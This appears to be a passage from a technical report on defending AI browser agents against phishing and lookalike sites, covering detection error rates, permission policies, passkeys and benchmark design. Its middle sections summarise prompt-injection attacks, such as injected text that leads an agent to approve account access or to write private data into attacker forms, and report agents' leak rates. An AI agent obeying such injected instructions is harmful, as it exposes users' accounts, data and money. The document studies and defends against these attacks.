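Agents open mostly harmless pages, so each of these signals may look accurate in a test where half of the sites are harmful and still raise mostly false alarms in use. Suppose, with invented round numbers, that an agent opens 10,000 pages, 5 of them harmful, and that a rule catches 70% of harmful pages and wrongly flags 1% of harmless ones. The rule will catch 3 or 4 harmful pages (5 × 0.70 = 3.5) and raise about 100 false alarms (9,995 × 0.01), so only about 3% of its alarms will be correct.

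Catching more of the harmful pages barely changes this. A rule that caught all five but still flagged 1% of harmless pages would be right in only about 5% of its alarms. For half of its alarms to be right, a rule that caught the original 70% of harmful pages could flag only about 0.035% of harmless pages, or one in 2,900.

The table applies some published error rates to the same invented 10,000 pages.

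| Method | Harmful pages caught, out of 5 | False alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Invented rule (70% caught, 1% wrongly flagged) | 3.5 | 100 |
| PhishSnap | 3.9 | About 2,000 |
| Hosting links alone, best model in *MANTIS* | 4.4 | About 1,280 |
| MANTIS, stricter threshold | 4.3 | 10 |

The table is only a rough comparison because each study used different sites. The MANTIS rates are for maliciously registered domains, so the figure of 4.3 catches applies only if none of the five harmful pages is on a hacked site or a free hosting service.

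False alarms can also take a long time to surface. Customers of the company that Liu and colleagues studied reported 123,491 suspected false alarms over six years, and its researchers accepted 98% of them. Half of the reports came more than 120 days after the detection. A short trial of a scoring system would have missed most of these complaints. (Some of the accepted reports concerned hacked sites that the system had flagged correctly but the owner had since cleaned.)

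Looking for evidence that a flagged site is legitimate can reduce false alarms. Liu and colleagues built IOBHunter, which uses a language model to search the web for other sites that support the flagged domain's legitimacy. It then looks for support for those sites in the same way, and continues until it reaches a government website or finds nothing more. If the flagged domain is a school's separate booking site, for example, the search might find a link to it on the school's page, and then a link to the school on the city's official page.

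In a two-month trial, IOBHunter found trusted evidence of a legitimate owner for 6,571 of about 15 million flagged domain names. Researchers confirmed that 4,338 of these were false alarms. Another 2,051 had been involved in malicious activity, so Liu and colleagues classed them as compromised. Proof of a legitimate owner is therefore not enough to call a page safe, since almost a third of the domains with such proof had been involved in malicious activity.

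### Sending an isolated agent to investigate

A system can also open the suspicious page and see what it does. Cloaking may show an ordinary scanner only a harmless page, or the scanner may see only a puzzle that visitors must solve first. *TraceScope* (Zhang, Reber and colleagues, 2026) uses two AI agents to get further than an ordinary scanner.

The first agent opens the address in a disposable browser, isolated from any real user's accounts. It behaves like a victim, using an invented name, password and payment card, and can click buttons, answer simple puzzles and fill in forms. Software records the screen and the network traffic. The second agent works from this recording and never visits the site. It goes through a checklist of attack techniques, such as capturing passwords, and must cite part of the recording for each finding. Analysts can therefore repeat the judgement after the site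 has gone.

Zhang and colleagues tested TraceScope on 241 phishing addresses and 467 harmless ones. It detected 78% of the phishing addresses, and 94% of the addresses it flagged were phishing. The best of three earlier systems that analysed a single snapshot of each page detected 25%. TraceScope detected all 12 pages in the test that requested something other than a login, such as access to a cryptocurrency wallet. It also detected a scam on Google Forms that requested a social security number, although the domain was trustworthy.

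The test excluded 292 of the original 1,000 addresses, mostly because the phishing content was already gone. This made the comparison fairer but also removed the shortest-lived attacks.

A two-week pilot gives a better idea of how TraceScope performs in practice. Security analysts submitted 111 suspicious addresses, of which 71 still worked. Eighteen of the 71 blocked an ordinary automated browser but opened for TraceScope. TraceScope found 30 of the 46 phishing sites (65%) and wrongly flagged 2 of the 25 harmless ones.

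The median investigation costs $0.24, but the most complicated 1% cost $1.73 or more. Browsing takes up to 60 seconds, and the second agent's review adds to that. Zhang and colleagues don't recommend TraceScope as a first filter for all web traffic. In the main test, it wrongly flagged about 2.6% of harmless addresses. At that rate, checking the hypothetical 10,000 pages would produce about 260 false alarms and cost about $2,400.

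TraceScope makes more sense as a second check. Suppose the invented rule flags 100 harmless pages and 3.5 harmful ones, and TraceScope investigates only those. At the pilot's error rates, it would clear 92 harmless pages and confirm 2.3 harmful ones, for about $25 at the median cost. False alarms would fall from 100 to 8, but so would the share of harmful pages caught, from 70% to 46%. These figures are uncertain because the pilot included only 25 harmless addresses and its analysts may have chosen different cases than a simple rule would.

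Attackers can adapt to this kind of inspection as well. TraceScope detected only 2 of the 12 phishing pages that were hidden behind CAPTCHAs and similar barriers. Some sites kept presenting new puzzles after it solved earlier ones. TraceScope's browser also reveals that it draws graphics in software instead of on a graphics card, so a site could recognise it and show it a harmless page.

The investigation can also interfere with the user's task. If the suspicious address is a genuine password-reset link that works only once, the isolated agent may use it up before the user's agent gets there. (This is an inference from how such links work, and Zhang and colleagues did not test it.)

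## Setting the rules for where an agent may go and what it may do

A navigation policy can limit what an agent does at sites whose safety is still unclear after the deployer has checked blocklists, allowlists and reputation scores. Refusing all these sites would make the agent useless for shopping and research, but allowing them all without limits would let in every new mirror. Kim and colleagues note that an agent's risk grows as it moves from answering questions to retrieving information and then to changing things, and as it gains access to sensitive data. The policy can therefore set few limits on reading and strict ones on signing in and paying.

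### What the task needs

The software can work out which sites and actions a request needs before the agent reads any web page. In ceLLMate, the browser extension built by Meng and colleagues, the model that lists a task's sites also picks from ready-made permissions for each one. If the user asks to view an Amazon basket "and checkout if the total is under 50 dollars", the model picks one permission to view the basket and another to order, with a limit of $50. An agent could get around that limit by placing two orders of $49, so the software can also count orders and allow only one.

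Three models picked the right permissions in at least 94% of tasks for each type of website. They did less well on 32 shopping tasks that also required a value, such as a spending limit, getting both the permissions and the value right in 81% to 97% of them. In one case, a model confused a wishlist with a shopping basket. When confirming the permissions, the user should check the spending limit most carefully.

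### What the agent may do at an unknown domain

A site that is on neither the task's list nor a blocklist needs its own rule for each action.

| Action at an unknown domain | What a bad site could gain | Suggested rule |
|---|---|---|
| Read, without the user's sessions | A chance to steer the agent | Allow |
| Type personal data | The data | Ask the user |
| Sign in | The password and the account | Allow only with a passkey or a password manager |
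| Give another service access to an account | Lasting access, without a password | Leave it to the user |
| Pay | Money and perhaps a card number | Refuse if the payee's real site is known; otherwise leave it to the user |
| Download a file | A way to run malware | Refuse, or open the file on a disposable machine |

Reading is the safest action if the agent uses a clean browser with no sessions, saved cards or access to the user's files, but it still carries some risk. Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues (2026) point out in *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* that an outright malicious site can do harm as soon as it loads, so the clean browser should run on a machine the deployer can discard.

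The rule on personal data has to apply before the agent types. A script on the page can send each character to the site's operator as it is typed, so a check when the agent clicks "Submit" comes too late. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (Iqbal, 2026) classes typing into another company's part of a page as irreversible, because that company can read the text.

The rule on account access covers an attack described in *The Agent Clicks Approve* (2026). In the example, a user asks an agent to read an update about a billing export and summarise the next steps. In an added note, an attacker claims that the export can't continue until someone clears an "access review", and tells the agent to choose the positive option there. The note links to a page where a service requests access to an account. If the agent clicks "Approve", the service gets access that the user never mentioned.

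*Building Browser Agents* argues for enforcing such limits in code rather than relying on the model's judgement. The simplest way to limit payments is to withhold the card number from the agent. According to Parker, Gemini in Chrome "will try to pause" before a purchase, which works only if the software recognises that a step is a purchase. An agent without a card number can't pay by card even if the software fails to recognise the purchase.

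### Checking again after a redirect and before a submission

A redirect can lead to a new domain, so the software has to apply the whole policy again. Permission to pay at a shop shouldn't carry over to a domain the shop redirects to unless the deployer has listed that domain too.

A form on one site can send its contents to another site, and the page's address doesn't show this. ceLLMate can detect it because it checks the browser's requests rather than the agent's clicks.

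Checking the blocklist again just before the agent types or pays takes little extra work. In a ten-minute task, the second check will rarely catch anything new, because a site often takes hours to appear on a blocklist. It is more useful if the page has been open in a tab since the morning.

The order total also needs a second check. Meng and colleagues found that Amazon's order request doesn't include the total, so their software, ceLLMate, has to read it from the page and remember it. If the agent changed the quantity and ordered before the page updated, ceLLMate would compare the old total with the spending limit. To prevent this, it makes each action wait until the previous one has taken full effect.

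### When a lookup service is down

A blocklist lookup can show that an address is listed, show that it isn't, or fail. If the software treats a failed lookup as "not on the list", the agent can open any address during an outage.

Stopping the agent at every failed lookup would be safe but annoying. Suppose one lookup in a thousand fails, independently of the others. A task with fifty pages would stop 4.9% of the time (1 − 0.999^50). If the agent stopped only when a lookup failed just before a payment, a task with one payment would stop 0.1% of the time. Real failures cluster because an outage can last minutes or hours, so the software should retry before returning the task to the user.

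The agent can therefore keep reading during an outage, using a stored copy of the blocklist that still catches older sites. It should wait until the outage ends before typing personal data, signing in, paying or downloading.

### What the agent does after a refusal

Some agents try another approach after a refusal. In Google's design, the model that rejects an action sends feedback to the planning model, which then makes a new plan. Parker adds that the agent can return the task to the user after repeated failures. OpenAI's address check may also prompt the agent to try another website.

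This is sensible when the first site was merely unsuitable, but an agent told to find another site may land on a mirror of the one it was refused. The mirror offers the same service under a similar name, so it fits the task equally well, and it may be too new for any blocklist. This is an inference, since none of these designs' makers report testing it. The risk grows with each attempt. If one in five alternatives were a mirror, an agent that tried three would have a 49% chance of opening at least one mirror (1 − 0.8^3).

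The software should tell the agent why it refused a site. If the site was unrelated to the task, the agent can look for another. If the site was on a phishing or gambling list, the agent should use only sites already on the task's list, or go back to the user. If the software has a screenshot of the refused site, it can also keep it to compare with the next page.

### Who may override a refusal

The agent should never be able to override a refusal. A user can reasonably approve an unknown site for one task, but approving a site on a phishing blocklist should take more than a click, because the attacker may already have persuaded the user that the site is genuine. Blocklists contain mistakes, so someone, such as a company administrator, has to be able to correct them. Google notes that an organisation's access and policy requirements already apply to employees signed in to Chrome. A private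 user who is sure that a site is safe can open it in an ordinary browser window and do that step without the agent.

An override should cover one domain and one action, and expire when the task ends. Otherwise, an agent allowed to read a shop's page on Monday could use that permission to pay there on Friday, when the domain has a new owner.

A person who has asked to be kept away from gambling shouldn't be able to override that rule on impulse. The software could delay the change by a day or require a second person's agreement.

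The request for an override also has to appear where the agent can't click it, such as in the browser's own interface or on the user's phone. An agent that clicks "Approve" on a web page because injected text recommends it might do the same with a prompt about its own actions. (This is an inference from the attack in *The Agent Clicks Approve*.)

### How many questions to ask the user

People who see many prompts tend to approve the next one from habit, so a policy should reserve prompts for the few steps where a mistake would do the most harm.

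Suppose a user asks an agent to find and buy a replacement dishwasher part. The agent uses a search engine, looks up the part number on the manufacturer's site, and reads a repair forum and a shop review site. It then compares five shops and buys from one, which uses a separate payment company. None of these sites is on an allowlist.

| Rule | Prompts | What the prompts concern |
|---|---|---|
| Ask at every new site | 10 | The search engine, the manufacturer, the forum, the review site, five shops and the payment company |
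| Ask before signing in or paying | 2 | Signing in at the chosen shop, and the payment |

With five such tasks a week, the first rule produces 50 prompts and the second produces 10. Under the first rule, the agent also uses its tenth prompt to ask whether it may open the payment company's site, but it doesn't ask about the more important step of spending $38. A user who read the first two prompts carefully and approved the rest from habit would have checked only the search engine and the manufacturer.

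The second rule has a drawback: the agent reads up to ten unfamiliar sites without asking, which is acceptable only in a clean browser. The rule also needs to cover downloads and personal data typed without signing in, such as a delivery address at a guest checkout.

Iqbal provides some evidence that a narrow rule needs few prompts. His software, INTACT, prompts the user only before acting on parts of a page that come from another company. It would have done so in 112 of 1,091 ordinary tasks on real web pages. Of those 112, 58 involved cookie dialogs, and in 22 the "other company" was the site itself under a second domain. Software that recognised those two cases would have prompted the user in only 32 tasks. Iqbal did not study how people answered the prompts.

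The prompt's wording also matters, because the user needs details to check and "Allow this site?" gives none. A prompt such as "Pay $38 at `parts.example`, where you have never bought anything?" includes the amount, the domain and the most useful warning sign, the lack of any earlier purchase there.

### Credentials that work only on the original site

Some protections work even when a lookalike site isn't on any blocklist and the user suspects nothing. A password manager stores each password with its site's domain and offers to fill it in only there. A lookalike has a different domain, so the password manager won't offer the password, however good the copy is.

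A passkey is stricter because there is no password to steal. When the user creates one, their device generates two matching keys, gives the site the public key and keeps the private one. To sign in, the site sends a random number, and the device signs it with the private key for that site's domain. The browser supplies the domain, so the page can't falsify it. A lookalike site could fetch a random number from the real site and pass it on, but the browser would still look for a key for the lookalike's domain and find none.

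These protections work only if the agent doesn't have the password. Parker explains that in Google's design, the user has to confirm before Chrome signs in with Google Password Manager, and the model has no direct access to stored passwords. An agent that finds a password in its instructions or in a document can type it anywhere. A site may also let people sign in with an emailed code instead of a passkey, and an agent that can read the user's email could enter that code on a lookalike site.

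If the password manager has no saved login for a site where the user supposedly has an account, the agent should stop. It shouldn't ask the user to type the password, which is what the AI browser Comet did on the fake Wells Fargo page. A missing login will sometimes be a false alarm, because companies do change domains or use a separate one for signing in.

Ordinary card numbers aren't tied to a particular site, which is why Comet could fill in a saved card at a fake Walmart. Some card issuers offer numbers that work at only one merchant or up to a set amount. If an agent pays a fake shop with a number that has a spending limit, the loss can't exceed that limit.

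Passkeys and password managers don't help if an attacker has taken over the real site, because its domain is still the right one.

### Keeping one site's content from directing actions on another

An agent can also carry information or instructions from one site to the next. Browsers normally prevent this with the same-origin policy, which stops a script on one origin (a combination of scheme, host name and port) from reading pages on another. But an agent remembers what it read on the first site while it types on the second.

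Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, measured how often this leaks data. Agents did a task involving private information, such as a shopping order or a bank account, then opened a page with injected instructions to write that information there. OpenAI's Atlas wrote exactly what the attacker wanted in 99 of 150 runs. On imitations of Google Forms, where the attacker could control the whole form, it did so in 29 of 30. A phishing site is most like these imitation forms, though an agent may also leak more on a form because it expects to fill in the fields.

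Wang and colleagues also built a defence, SOPGuard, which labels everything the agent reads with the site it came from. A summary or calculation inherits the labels of the data behind it. If the agent is about to type something labelled with another site, the software asks the user first. This reduced the leaks to zero in their tests, but only because a prompt counts as preventing the leak. A user who approves from habit would still let the data through. A card number that the user typed into the request apparently gets no label, so SOPGuard would not ask about it. (This is an inference from the labelling rules.)

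None of the five malicious-page detectors that Wang and colleagues tried was accurate enough to replace rules for the agent, although detection would be simpler. WARD missed at most 2% of the pages with injected text but flagged 26% to 47% of clean pages. BrowseSafe missed 41% to 64% of malicious pages.

Other designs restrict what the agent sees or does on a page. *Prismata* (Villa, Ozdarendeli and colleagues, 2026) uses a model to decide which buttons and links the task needs. For each one, the model receives only that element and the sections of the page that contain it, so an instruction in a product review can't influence a decision about the "change password" button. Another step looks for signs of outside content, such as a "Reviews" heading, before reading the content below. The software then hides the outside content or makes it read-only.

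The main test of Prismata used pop-ups that tried to lure the agent to a malicious website, which is also how an agent might reach a new mirror. Prismata cut the success rate of these attacks from 85.5% to 0.7%. Under attack, the agent completed 23.0% of its tasks with Prismata and 4.5% without it. When there was no attack, Prismata reduced the share of tasks completed from 29.9% to 26.6%, a drop of about one-ninth.

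Nikolić and colleagues replace content that the site's owner can't vouch for with labelled blanks. If the agent needs something from a blank, a second model reads the hidden text and may return only a yes or no, a number, a date or a choice from a list. It can report that a review gives four stars, but it can't pass on an instruction to visit another site.

Iqbal's INTACT shows the model one element of the page at a time, so text in an advertisement can affect only what the agent does with that advertisement. It also records which company's script created each element. A browser's own records often lack this information, and they attributed 58.7% of other companies' elements to the site itself. To simulate an agent that an attacker had fully persuaded, Iqbal told the model to obey injected instructions. A conventional agent then followed 73.1% of the attacks. With INTACT, 12.8% got through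 the planning, and these could at most lead to a request for the user's consent.

These protections differ in what they cost.

| Source | Design | Effect on completed tasks | Other costs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Parker | Chrome's limits on which sites Gemini may read or act on | No figure published | No figure published |
| Meng and colleagues | ceLLMate | Not measured | Pages load 7% to 15% more slowly |
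| Wang and colleagues | SOPGuard | No significant change | Tasks take 2% to 6% longer |
| Villa and colleagues | Prismata | 26.6% completed instead of 29.9% | Model costs rise by about 47% |
| Nikolić and colleagues | Masked content | Little or no loss | 1.05 to 1.84 times the cost per task |
| Iqbal | INTACT | 3.7% of plans lose a needed function | Planning takes 34 times as long |

INTACT's real loss may be higher than 3.7%, because the plans were never carried out. A language model judged them instead, and it gave no clear verdict on roughly a third. Among the rest, it approved 85% of INTACT's plans and 92% of the conventional ones. INTACT's median planning time was 83 seconds, compared with 2.5 for conventional planning, though Iqbal estimates that running the model's decisions in parallel would reduce it to 12.5.

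Google's first release was simpler than its published design because it didn't yet keep a separate list of sites that Gemini may read but not act on.

Prismata, masking and INTACT all assume that the site's owner is honest. They can stop an advertisement or a review on an honest site from sending the agent to a lookalike. They offer much less protection on the lookalike, because the attacker wrote the whole page, including any headings that Prismata relies on. Nikolić and colleagues suggest using their method with an allowlist of trusted domains, and weaker defences elsewhere. Chrome's design and ceLLMate can keep a lookalike from sending the agent to the user's email or bank, provided the task doesn't include those sites.

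### Paying an energy bill

Suppose a user asks an agent to pay this month's energy bill, which has arrived by email. The supplier's real site is `energy.example`, and the user's bills are usually about $60. The email is from a phisher, and it links to `energy-bills.example`, which the phisher registered yesterday and which isn't on any blocklist.

1. The software works out what the task needs. The agent may read the user's email, sign in at `energy.example` and make one payment of up to $100. The supplier's domain comes from the user's password manager, which has an entry from earlier visits. The user confirms the sites and the limit.
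2. The agent finds the email, which demands $84.20 by tonight. Its link goes through a tracking service and then redirects to `energy-bills.example`. The software checks both domains and finds neither on a blocklist or on the task's list. The agent may therefore read the page, but only in a clean browser.
3. The page is a good copy of the supplier's site and shows the same $84.20. The model concludes that the page fits the task, and a separate relevance check might well agree. Neither opinion gives the agent permission to type anything.
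4. The page has a login form. The password manager offers nothing for this domain, and the agent has no password to enter. The page also lets customers pay as a guest with an account number and a card. The software refuses, because the task allows payment only at `energy.example`. It doesn't ask the user to approve an exception, since somebody who expects to pay an energy bill might say yes without noticing the domain.
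5. The software tells the agent why it refused and forbids it to search for another payment page, because a search could lead to a second copy. The agent instead opens `energy.example` from the task's list.
6. The user approves the sign-in, and the password manager fills in the password. The account shows a bill of $61.75, due in two weeks, and nothing overdue.
7. The agent reports that the email and the account disagree. The software repeats the blocklist lookup and then asks whether to pay $61.75 at `energy.example`. If the lookup service is down, the payment waits, which does no harm with two weeks left. The user approves the payment, and the browser supplies the card details without showing them to the model.

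The user has answered three questions without being asked whether to trust `energy-bills.example`. The deployer can also report that domain to a blocklist, which may protect the phisher's other targets sooner.

The example works because the software had the supplier's real domain on record before the agent read the email. If a new customer has no saved entry, the agent shouldn't take the domain from the message that asks for money. The contract or a printed bill is a better source. If the user had saved `energy-bills.example` as the supplier's site by mistake, the password manager would offer the password there and the software would allow the payment.

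## Testing protection against new domains

The easiest test of a navigation policy, counting how many phishing addresses from a public blocklist the agent opens, mostly shows whether the agent has a working list that includes the same addresses. It doesn't show whether that list adds new addresses soon enough, because somebody had already found and reported every address in the test. A list that adds every phishing page nine hours after the page's first visitor would score 100% on day-old addresses, even if most of the victims had come in those nine hours.

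### Launching harmless phishing sites

Testers who launch their own test sites know when each site went online and that no blocklist contains it yet. For *PhishTime* (2020), Oest, Safaei and colleagues launched 2,862 harmless copies of PayPal's login page, with PayPal's permission, in six rounds over nine months. They reported the sites and measured each browser blocklist's speed (the time from report to block) and coverage (the share of sites blocked within a week).

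The researchers first studied 4,393 real phishing addresses to learn which tricks delayed blocking, then copied those tricks. They launched sites in batches of 54, a size they chose with a statistical power calculation, and changed only one feature between the batches they compared. They registered the domains six months ahead and built the names from random English words, so that neither age nor wording would make the sites look suspicious. Forty virtual machines checked every site at least every ten minutes. The sites showed these machines a harmless page, so the checks could not alert a blocklist.

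The table gives the average results for Google Safe Browsing.

| Test sites | Coverage | Median time to block |
|---|---|---|
| No evasion, desktop Chrome | 92.9% | 57 minutes |
| No evasion, mobile Chrome | 57.8% | 17 hours 30 minutes |
| Behind a `bit.ly` link, desktop Chrome | 86.1% | 2 hours 58 minutes |
| Behind a CAPTCHA, desktop Chrome | 0% | Never blocked |
| Shown only after a mouse movement, desktop Chrome | 0% | Never blocked |

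Redirects clearly slowed blocklisting, but their effect on coverage is less certain because the researchers tested them only in the first four rounds, when coverage of the plain sites averaged 90.7%. Two products can use the same list and still protect their users very differently, as desktop and mobile Chrome did.

In the third round, coverage of the plain sites fell to 64.8%, after 100% in each of the first two. The researchers relaunched the test and got a similar result. PayPal's crawler had apparently stopped visiting most of the sites reported to it, and PayPal later fixed it. Because the failure was temporary, a single test would have missed it if run in May 2019, or made the list look permanently bad if run in September.

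The blocklisting speeds in *PhishTime* date from 2019 and are for sites that the researchers reported immediately to Google, APWG and several others, so they exclude the hours before anyone reports a page. When the researchers reported sites only to PayPal, Safe Browsing covered 16.2% of them.

Two later studies measured real sites instead of launching their own. *PhishLang* (2024) used a detector to find phishing sites, reported the ones that blocklists had missed, and then checked the blocklists again. Safe Browsing's coverage of sites that hid behind JavaScript rose from 35% to 73%. *ReDence* (2026) used a similar method on 4,042 scam sites. Safe Browsing listed 16.3% of them before the reports and 33.0% within seven days afterwards, while the share listed by Microsoft's SmartScreen rose from 15.2% to 31.3%.

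These studies show large gaps on real sites, but they don't show how much of the increase the reports caused. Safe Browsing added about 675 of the sites in *ReDence*, and Google confirmed that the reports had helped with 83. Google may have found many of the others without the reports. Leaving half of the sites unreported would have shown how much the reports helped, but real people would have been harmed. Testing with harmless copies avoids that problem.

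### Two tests of browsers

AV-Comparatives' *Anti-Phishing Comparative Test* (2025) opened 250 phishing pages and 250 legitimate ones in six browsers between 1 and 11 November 2025. No browser blocked a legitimate page. At least three vendors supported the test, but the laboratory chose the dates and did not disclose them in advance.

In 2025, LayerX, a browser security company, ran a test using the 100 most recent phishing pages listed on OpenPhish, PhishTank and similar sites. The pages came from public lists, so the test has the weakness described above. LayerX also sells a competing product, which it says identified 98% of the phishing pages. The company reports no test on legitimate pages, so the product's false alarm rate is unknown.

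AV-Comparatives has since repeated its test, and its *Single Product Tests and Reviews* lists three rounds in 2026. NordVPN (2026) confirms that the first ran from 7 to 19 January with 250 phishing addresses. The blog post *Microsoft Edge* (2026) gives browser scores for that round, but they are second-hand and deserve less trust than the 2025 scores. TechRadar's *NordVPN's antivirus tool blocks 94% of phishing sites in latest independent test* (2026) covers the August round but gives no browser scores.

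| Browser | AV-Comparatives, January 2025 | AV-Comparatives, November 2025 | AV-Comparatives, January 2026 | LayerX, 2025 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Chrome | 70% | 41% | 72% | 47% |
| Edge | 73% | 65% | 70% | 54% |
| Firefox | 70% | 74% | 75% | Not tested |
| Opera | 45% | 74% | 74% | Not tested |
| Avast Secure Browser | 94% | 85% | Not reported | Not tested |
| Norton Secure Browser | 94% | 85% | Not reported | Not tested |
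| Dia | Not tested | Not tested | Not tested | 46% |
| Comet | Not tested | Not tested | Not tested | 7% |
| Genspark | Not tested | Not tested | Not tested | 7% |

LayerX opened pages in the AI browsers Dia, Comet and Genspark but did not give their agents tasks. Dia and Chrome gave the same result on 97% of the pages, so Dia almost certainly used Google's list. Comet and Genspark blocked pages only because of faulty encryption certificates. In a later LayerX test, described in eSecurity Planet's *LayerX Exposes Critical Flaw in OpenAI’s ChatGPT Atlas Browser*, OpenAI's Atlas blocked 6 of 103 phishing pages.

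Firefox's lead over Chrome in November is odd, because Firefox relies mainly on Google's list. When the consumer organisation Which? found a similar gap in an earlier test, Google replied that browsers with the same technology were unlikely to differ much. *PhishTime* supports that claim, since desktop Firefox and Chrome had the same coverage and Firefox was only about ten minutes slower. A difference in settings or the timing of visits might explain the November gap.

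### How much a hundred pages can show

Chrome's 47 out of 100 is an estimate of how it would do on all pages of this kind. The 95% margin of error is 1.96 × √(0.47 × 0.53 / 100), or about 10 percentage points, so the true figure could reasonably be anywhere from 37% to 57%.

When two browsers are tested on the same pages, only the pages where their results differ help show which is better. LayerX reports that Edge did better on about 14 pages and Chrome on about 6. If the browsers were equally good, each would be equally likely to do better on any of these pages, and a split at least this uneven, in either direction, would happen about 12% of the time, so Edge's lead could easily be chance. LayerX would have needed to test about 235 pages to have an 80% chance of detecting a difference of this size.

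Chance is very unlikely to explain the gap between Chrome and Comet. Even if the two had blocked entirely different pages, Chrome alone would have blocked 47 and Comet alone 7, and equally good browsers would produce a split that uneven less than once in ten million tests.

These calculations assume the pages are independent, but pages from the same phishing campaign tend to produce the same test result. Suppose the 100 pages came from 20 campaigns of five pages each, with a correlation of 0.5 between pages of the same campaign. They would be equivalent to only about 33 independent pages (100 / (1 + 4 × 0.5)), and the margin of error would grow from 10 points to 17.

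Even if a test of n independent cases produces no failures, the true failure rate could be as high as about 3/n.

| Independent cases | Margin for a result near 50% | Highest plausible failure rate after no failures |
|---|---|---|
| 54 | 13 points | 5.4% |
| 100 | 10 points | 3.0% |
| 250 | 6 points | 1.2% |
| 1,000 | 3 points | 0.3% |

AV-Comparatives found no false alarms on 250 legitimate pages, but the true rate could still be 1.2%, or 120 false alarms in 10,000 pages.

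A result can go out of date even if the sample is large. In November 2025, Edge beat Chrome by 24 points, far more than chance would explain with 250 pages. Two months later, Chrome was 2 points ahead. Google may have improved its protection, or the January pages may have suited Chrome better.

### Building a test for an agent

A deployer can test how the rules handle unlisted domains by building harmless sites under invented names on a closed network, which keeps them off blocklists. Testing whether blocklists add new domains quickly enough requires the agent to visit real phishing pages soon after they appear, from a disposable machine with invented accounts.

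Both tests should use the complete agent. *Harness Matters* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) found that GPT-4o resisted 84% of attacks in one agent program and 43% in another. The agent also has to reach the page the way it normally would, since the browser's phishing warnings may not stop the agent.

**Splitting by time and campaign.** The deployer should set every rule and threshold using sites that appeared before a cutoff date, and test only on sites that appeared later. With a random split, some of the later sites would be used to set the rules.

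All the sites of one campaign should also go on the same side of the split. A rule based on ten of the `wonaco` domains that Australia blocked will do very well on the other eleven, but that result won't show whether the rule can catch the next casino's sites. Shared servers, page templates, redirect links and payment details can help group sites. If it's unclear whether sites are related, it is safer to keep them together.

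**Choosing the cases.** The test should include new domains that phishers bought, hacked sites, pages on free hosting services, mirrors of blocked casinos and redirects from allowed sites, with a separate result for each. It should also include scams that don't ask for a password, since Safe Browsing initially listed 44.1% of the password-stealing sites in *ReDence* but only 7.9% of the others.

Some test pages should contain no persuasive text. One of the *Harness Matters* pages had only a credit card field in a course registration form. Pages like this, with no injected instruction or sales pitch, worked about as well against some agents as openly manipulative ones, perhaps because they contained nothing that looked like an attack.

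An unprotected control browser should open each page just before and after the agent does, to confirm that the page works. Otherwise, dead pages count as successful blocks. If 30 of 100 pages are dead and the agent blocks 35 of the 70 live ones, it has blocked 50% of the live pages, but counting the dead pages as blocked gives 65%.

The control browser should connect from the kind of IP address a victim would have, in case the site is cloaked. If the control browser gets the phishing page and the agent doesn't, cloaking may have protected the agent. The deployer should count such cases separately, since the site's operator can change the cloaking at any time.

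**Pairing harmful and legitimate tasks.** An agent can avoid every phishing page by doing nothing, so a low leak rate can be misleading unless the test also measures whether the agent completes legitimate tasks. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, 2026) pairs each phishing case in its two main tests with the same task on the genuine site. When a user asked it to sign in, Claude Opus 4.8 leaked account details in 31.2% of phishing cases and failed to submit the form in 6.6% of legitimate ones. When it was sorting an inbox and had not been asked to sign in, it leaked details in 1.8% of phishing cases but failed to submit the form in 88.3% of legitimate ones.

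Pairs also show whether a defence reduces leaks without blocking legitimate tasks. Ahmed and colleagues gave the models the services' real domains and told them to compare these with the domain of the site they were on. In the sign-in test, this cut GPT-5-mini's leak rate from 71.9% to 22.4% and raised the share of legitimate tasks it completed by 23.4 percentage points.

A related mistake is to count it as a defence when an agent fails to hand over a card number only because it can't operate the form. In *Harness Matters*, Wu and colleagues therefore counted a defence only if the agent could complete a harmless version of the same task. By this measure, one program, Agent-E, fell for 20% of the attacks. Counting every failed attack as a defence would have lowered the figure to 12%.

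The web page should record what the agent typed and clicked, as it did in *Harness Matters*, because an agent may misreport what it did. This also works for commercial agents whose internal records testers can't see. Claude Computer Use, running on the small model Claude Haiku 4.5, fell for 22% of the deceptive pages, and Gemini Computer Use fell for 26%.

An agent can treat the same page differently each time, as Comet did with Guardio's fake shop, so each case needs several runs. Overall rates can be steadier than single cases. *Harness Matters* ran its whole benchmark three times with two models, and the standard deviation of the results averaged only 1.7 points. But repeated runs don't increase the number of sites tested, so ten runs on each of 30 sites is still a test of 30 sites.

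The whole test should run again on fresh sites every month or quarter, and after any change to the model, the browser or the lists. It also helps to include a few sites that never change. If the agent does worse on those, the agent is probably the cause, whereas a drop only on fresh sites suggests the attackers or the lists have changed.

### What to report

A single block rate hides most of what a deployer needs to know.

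| Measure | How to calculate it |
|---|---|
| Blocked on first visit | Share of live harmful pages that the agent's software blocked as soon as the tester found them |
| Blocked later | The same share after 1, 6 and 24 hours |
| Listing delay | Median time until a list added the site, with the share not listed within a week |
| Unsafe actions | Share of harmful cases in which the agent gave away data, paid or downloaded a file, leaving out tasks it can't do |
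| False refusals | Share of legitimate cases in which the agent or its software refused a necessary step |
| Finished tasks | Share of legitimate tasks completed |
| Recovery | Share of tasks that the agent finished on the genuine site after meeting a fake one, without leaking anything |
| Prompts | Average number of questions to the user per task |

*Web Browser Security Comparative Test Report* (NSS Labs, 2020) gave a separate "zero-hour" block rate for phishing pages that were new to the test. Edge blocked 95.5% of phishing addresses overall, but its zero-hour rate was 89.2%.

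Recovery is the hardest of these measures for current agents. In *CredLeakBench*, an agent had to ignore a phishing link and sign in through the genuine address, which it could find in the user's records. GPT-5-mini did best, succeeding in 27.7% of cases. Opus 4.8 leaked nothing but never reached the genuine site. A policy that sends the agent to a stored address after a refusal should do better, and measuring recovery would test this.

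Each result should include the number of independent campaigns tested. To show that an agent takes an unsafe action in fewer than about 1% of campaigns, a deployer needs roughly 300 campaigns with no failures. Few companies will find that many real campaigns in a month. They can combine several months to estimate the overall rate, as long as the agent hasn't changed much, and check the smaller monthly samples for a sudden drop like the one in *PhishTime*'s third round.
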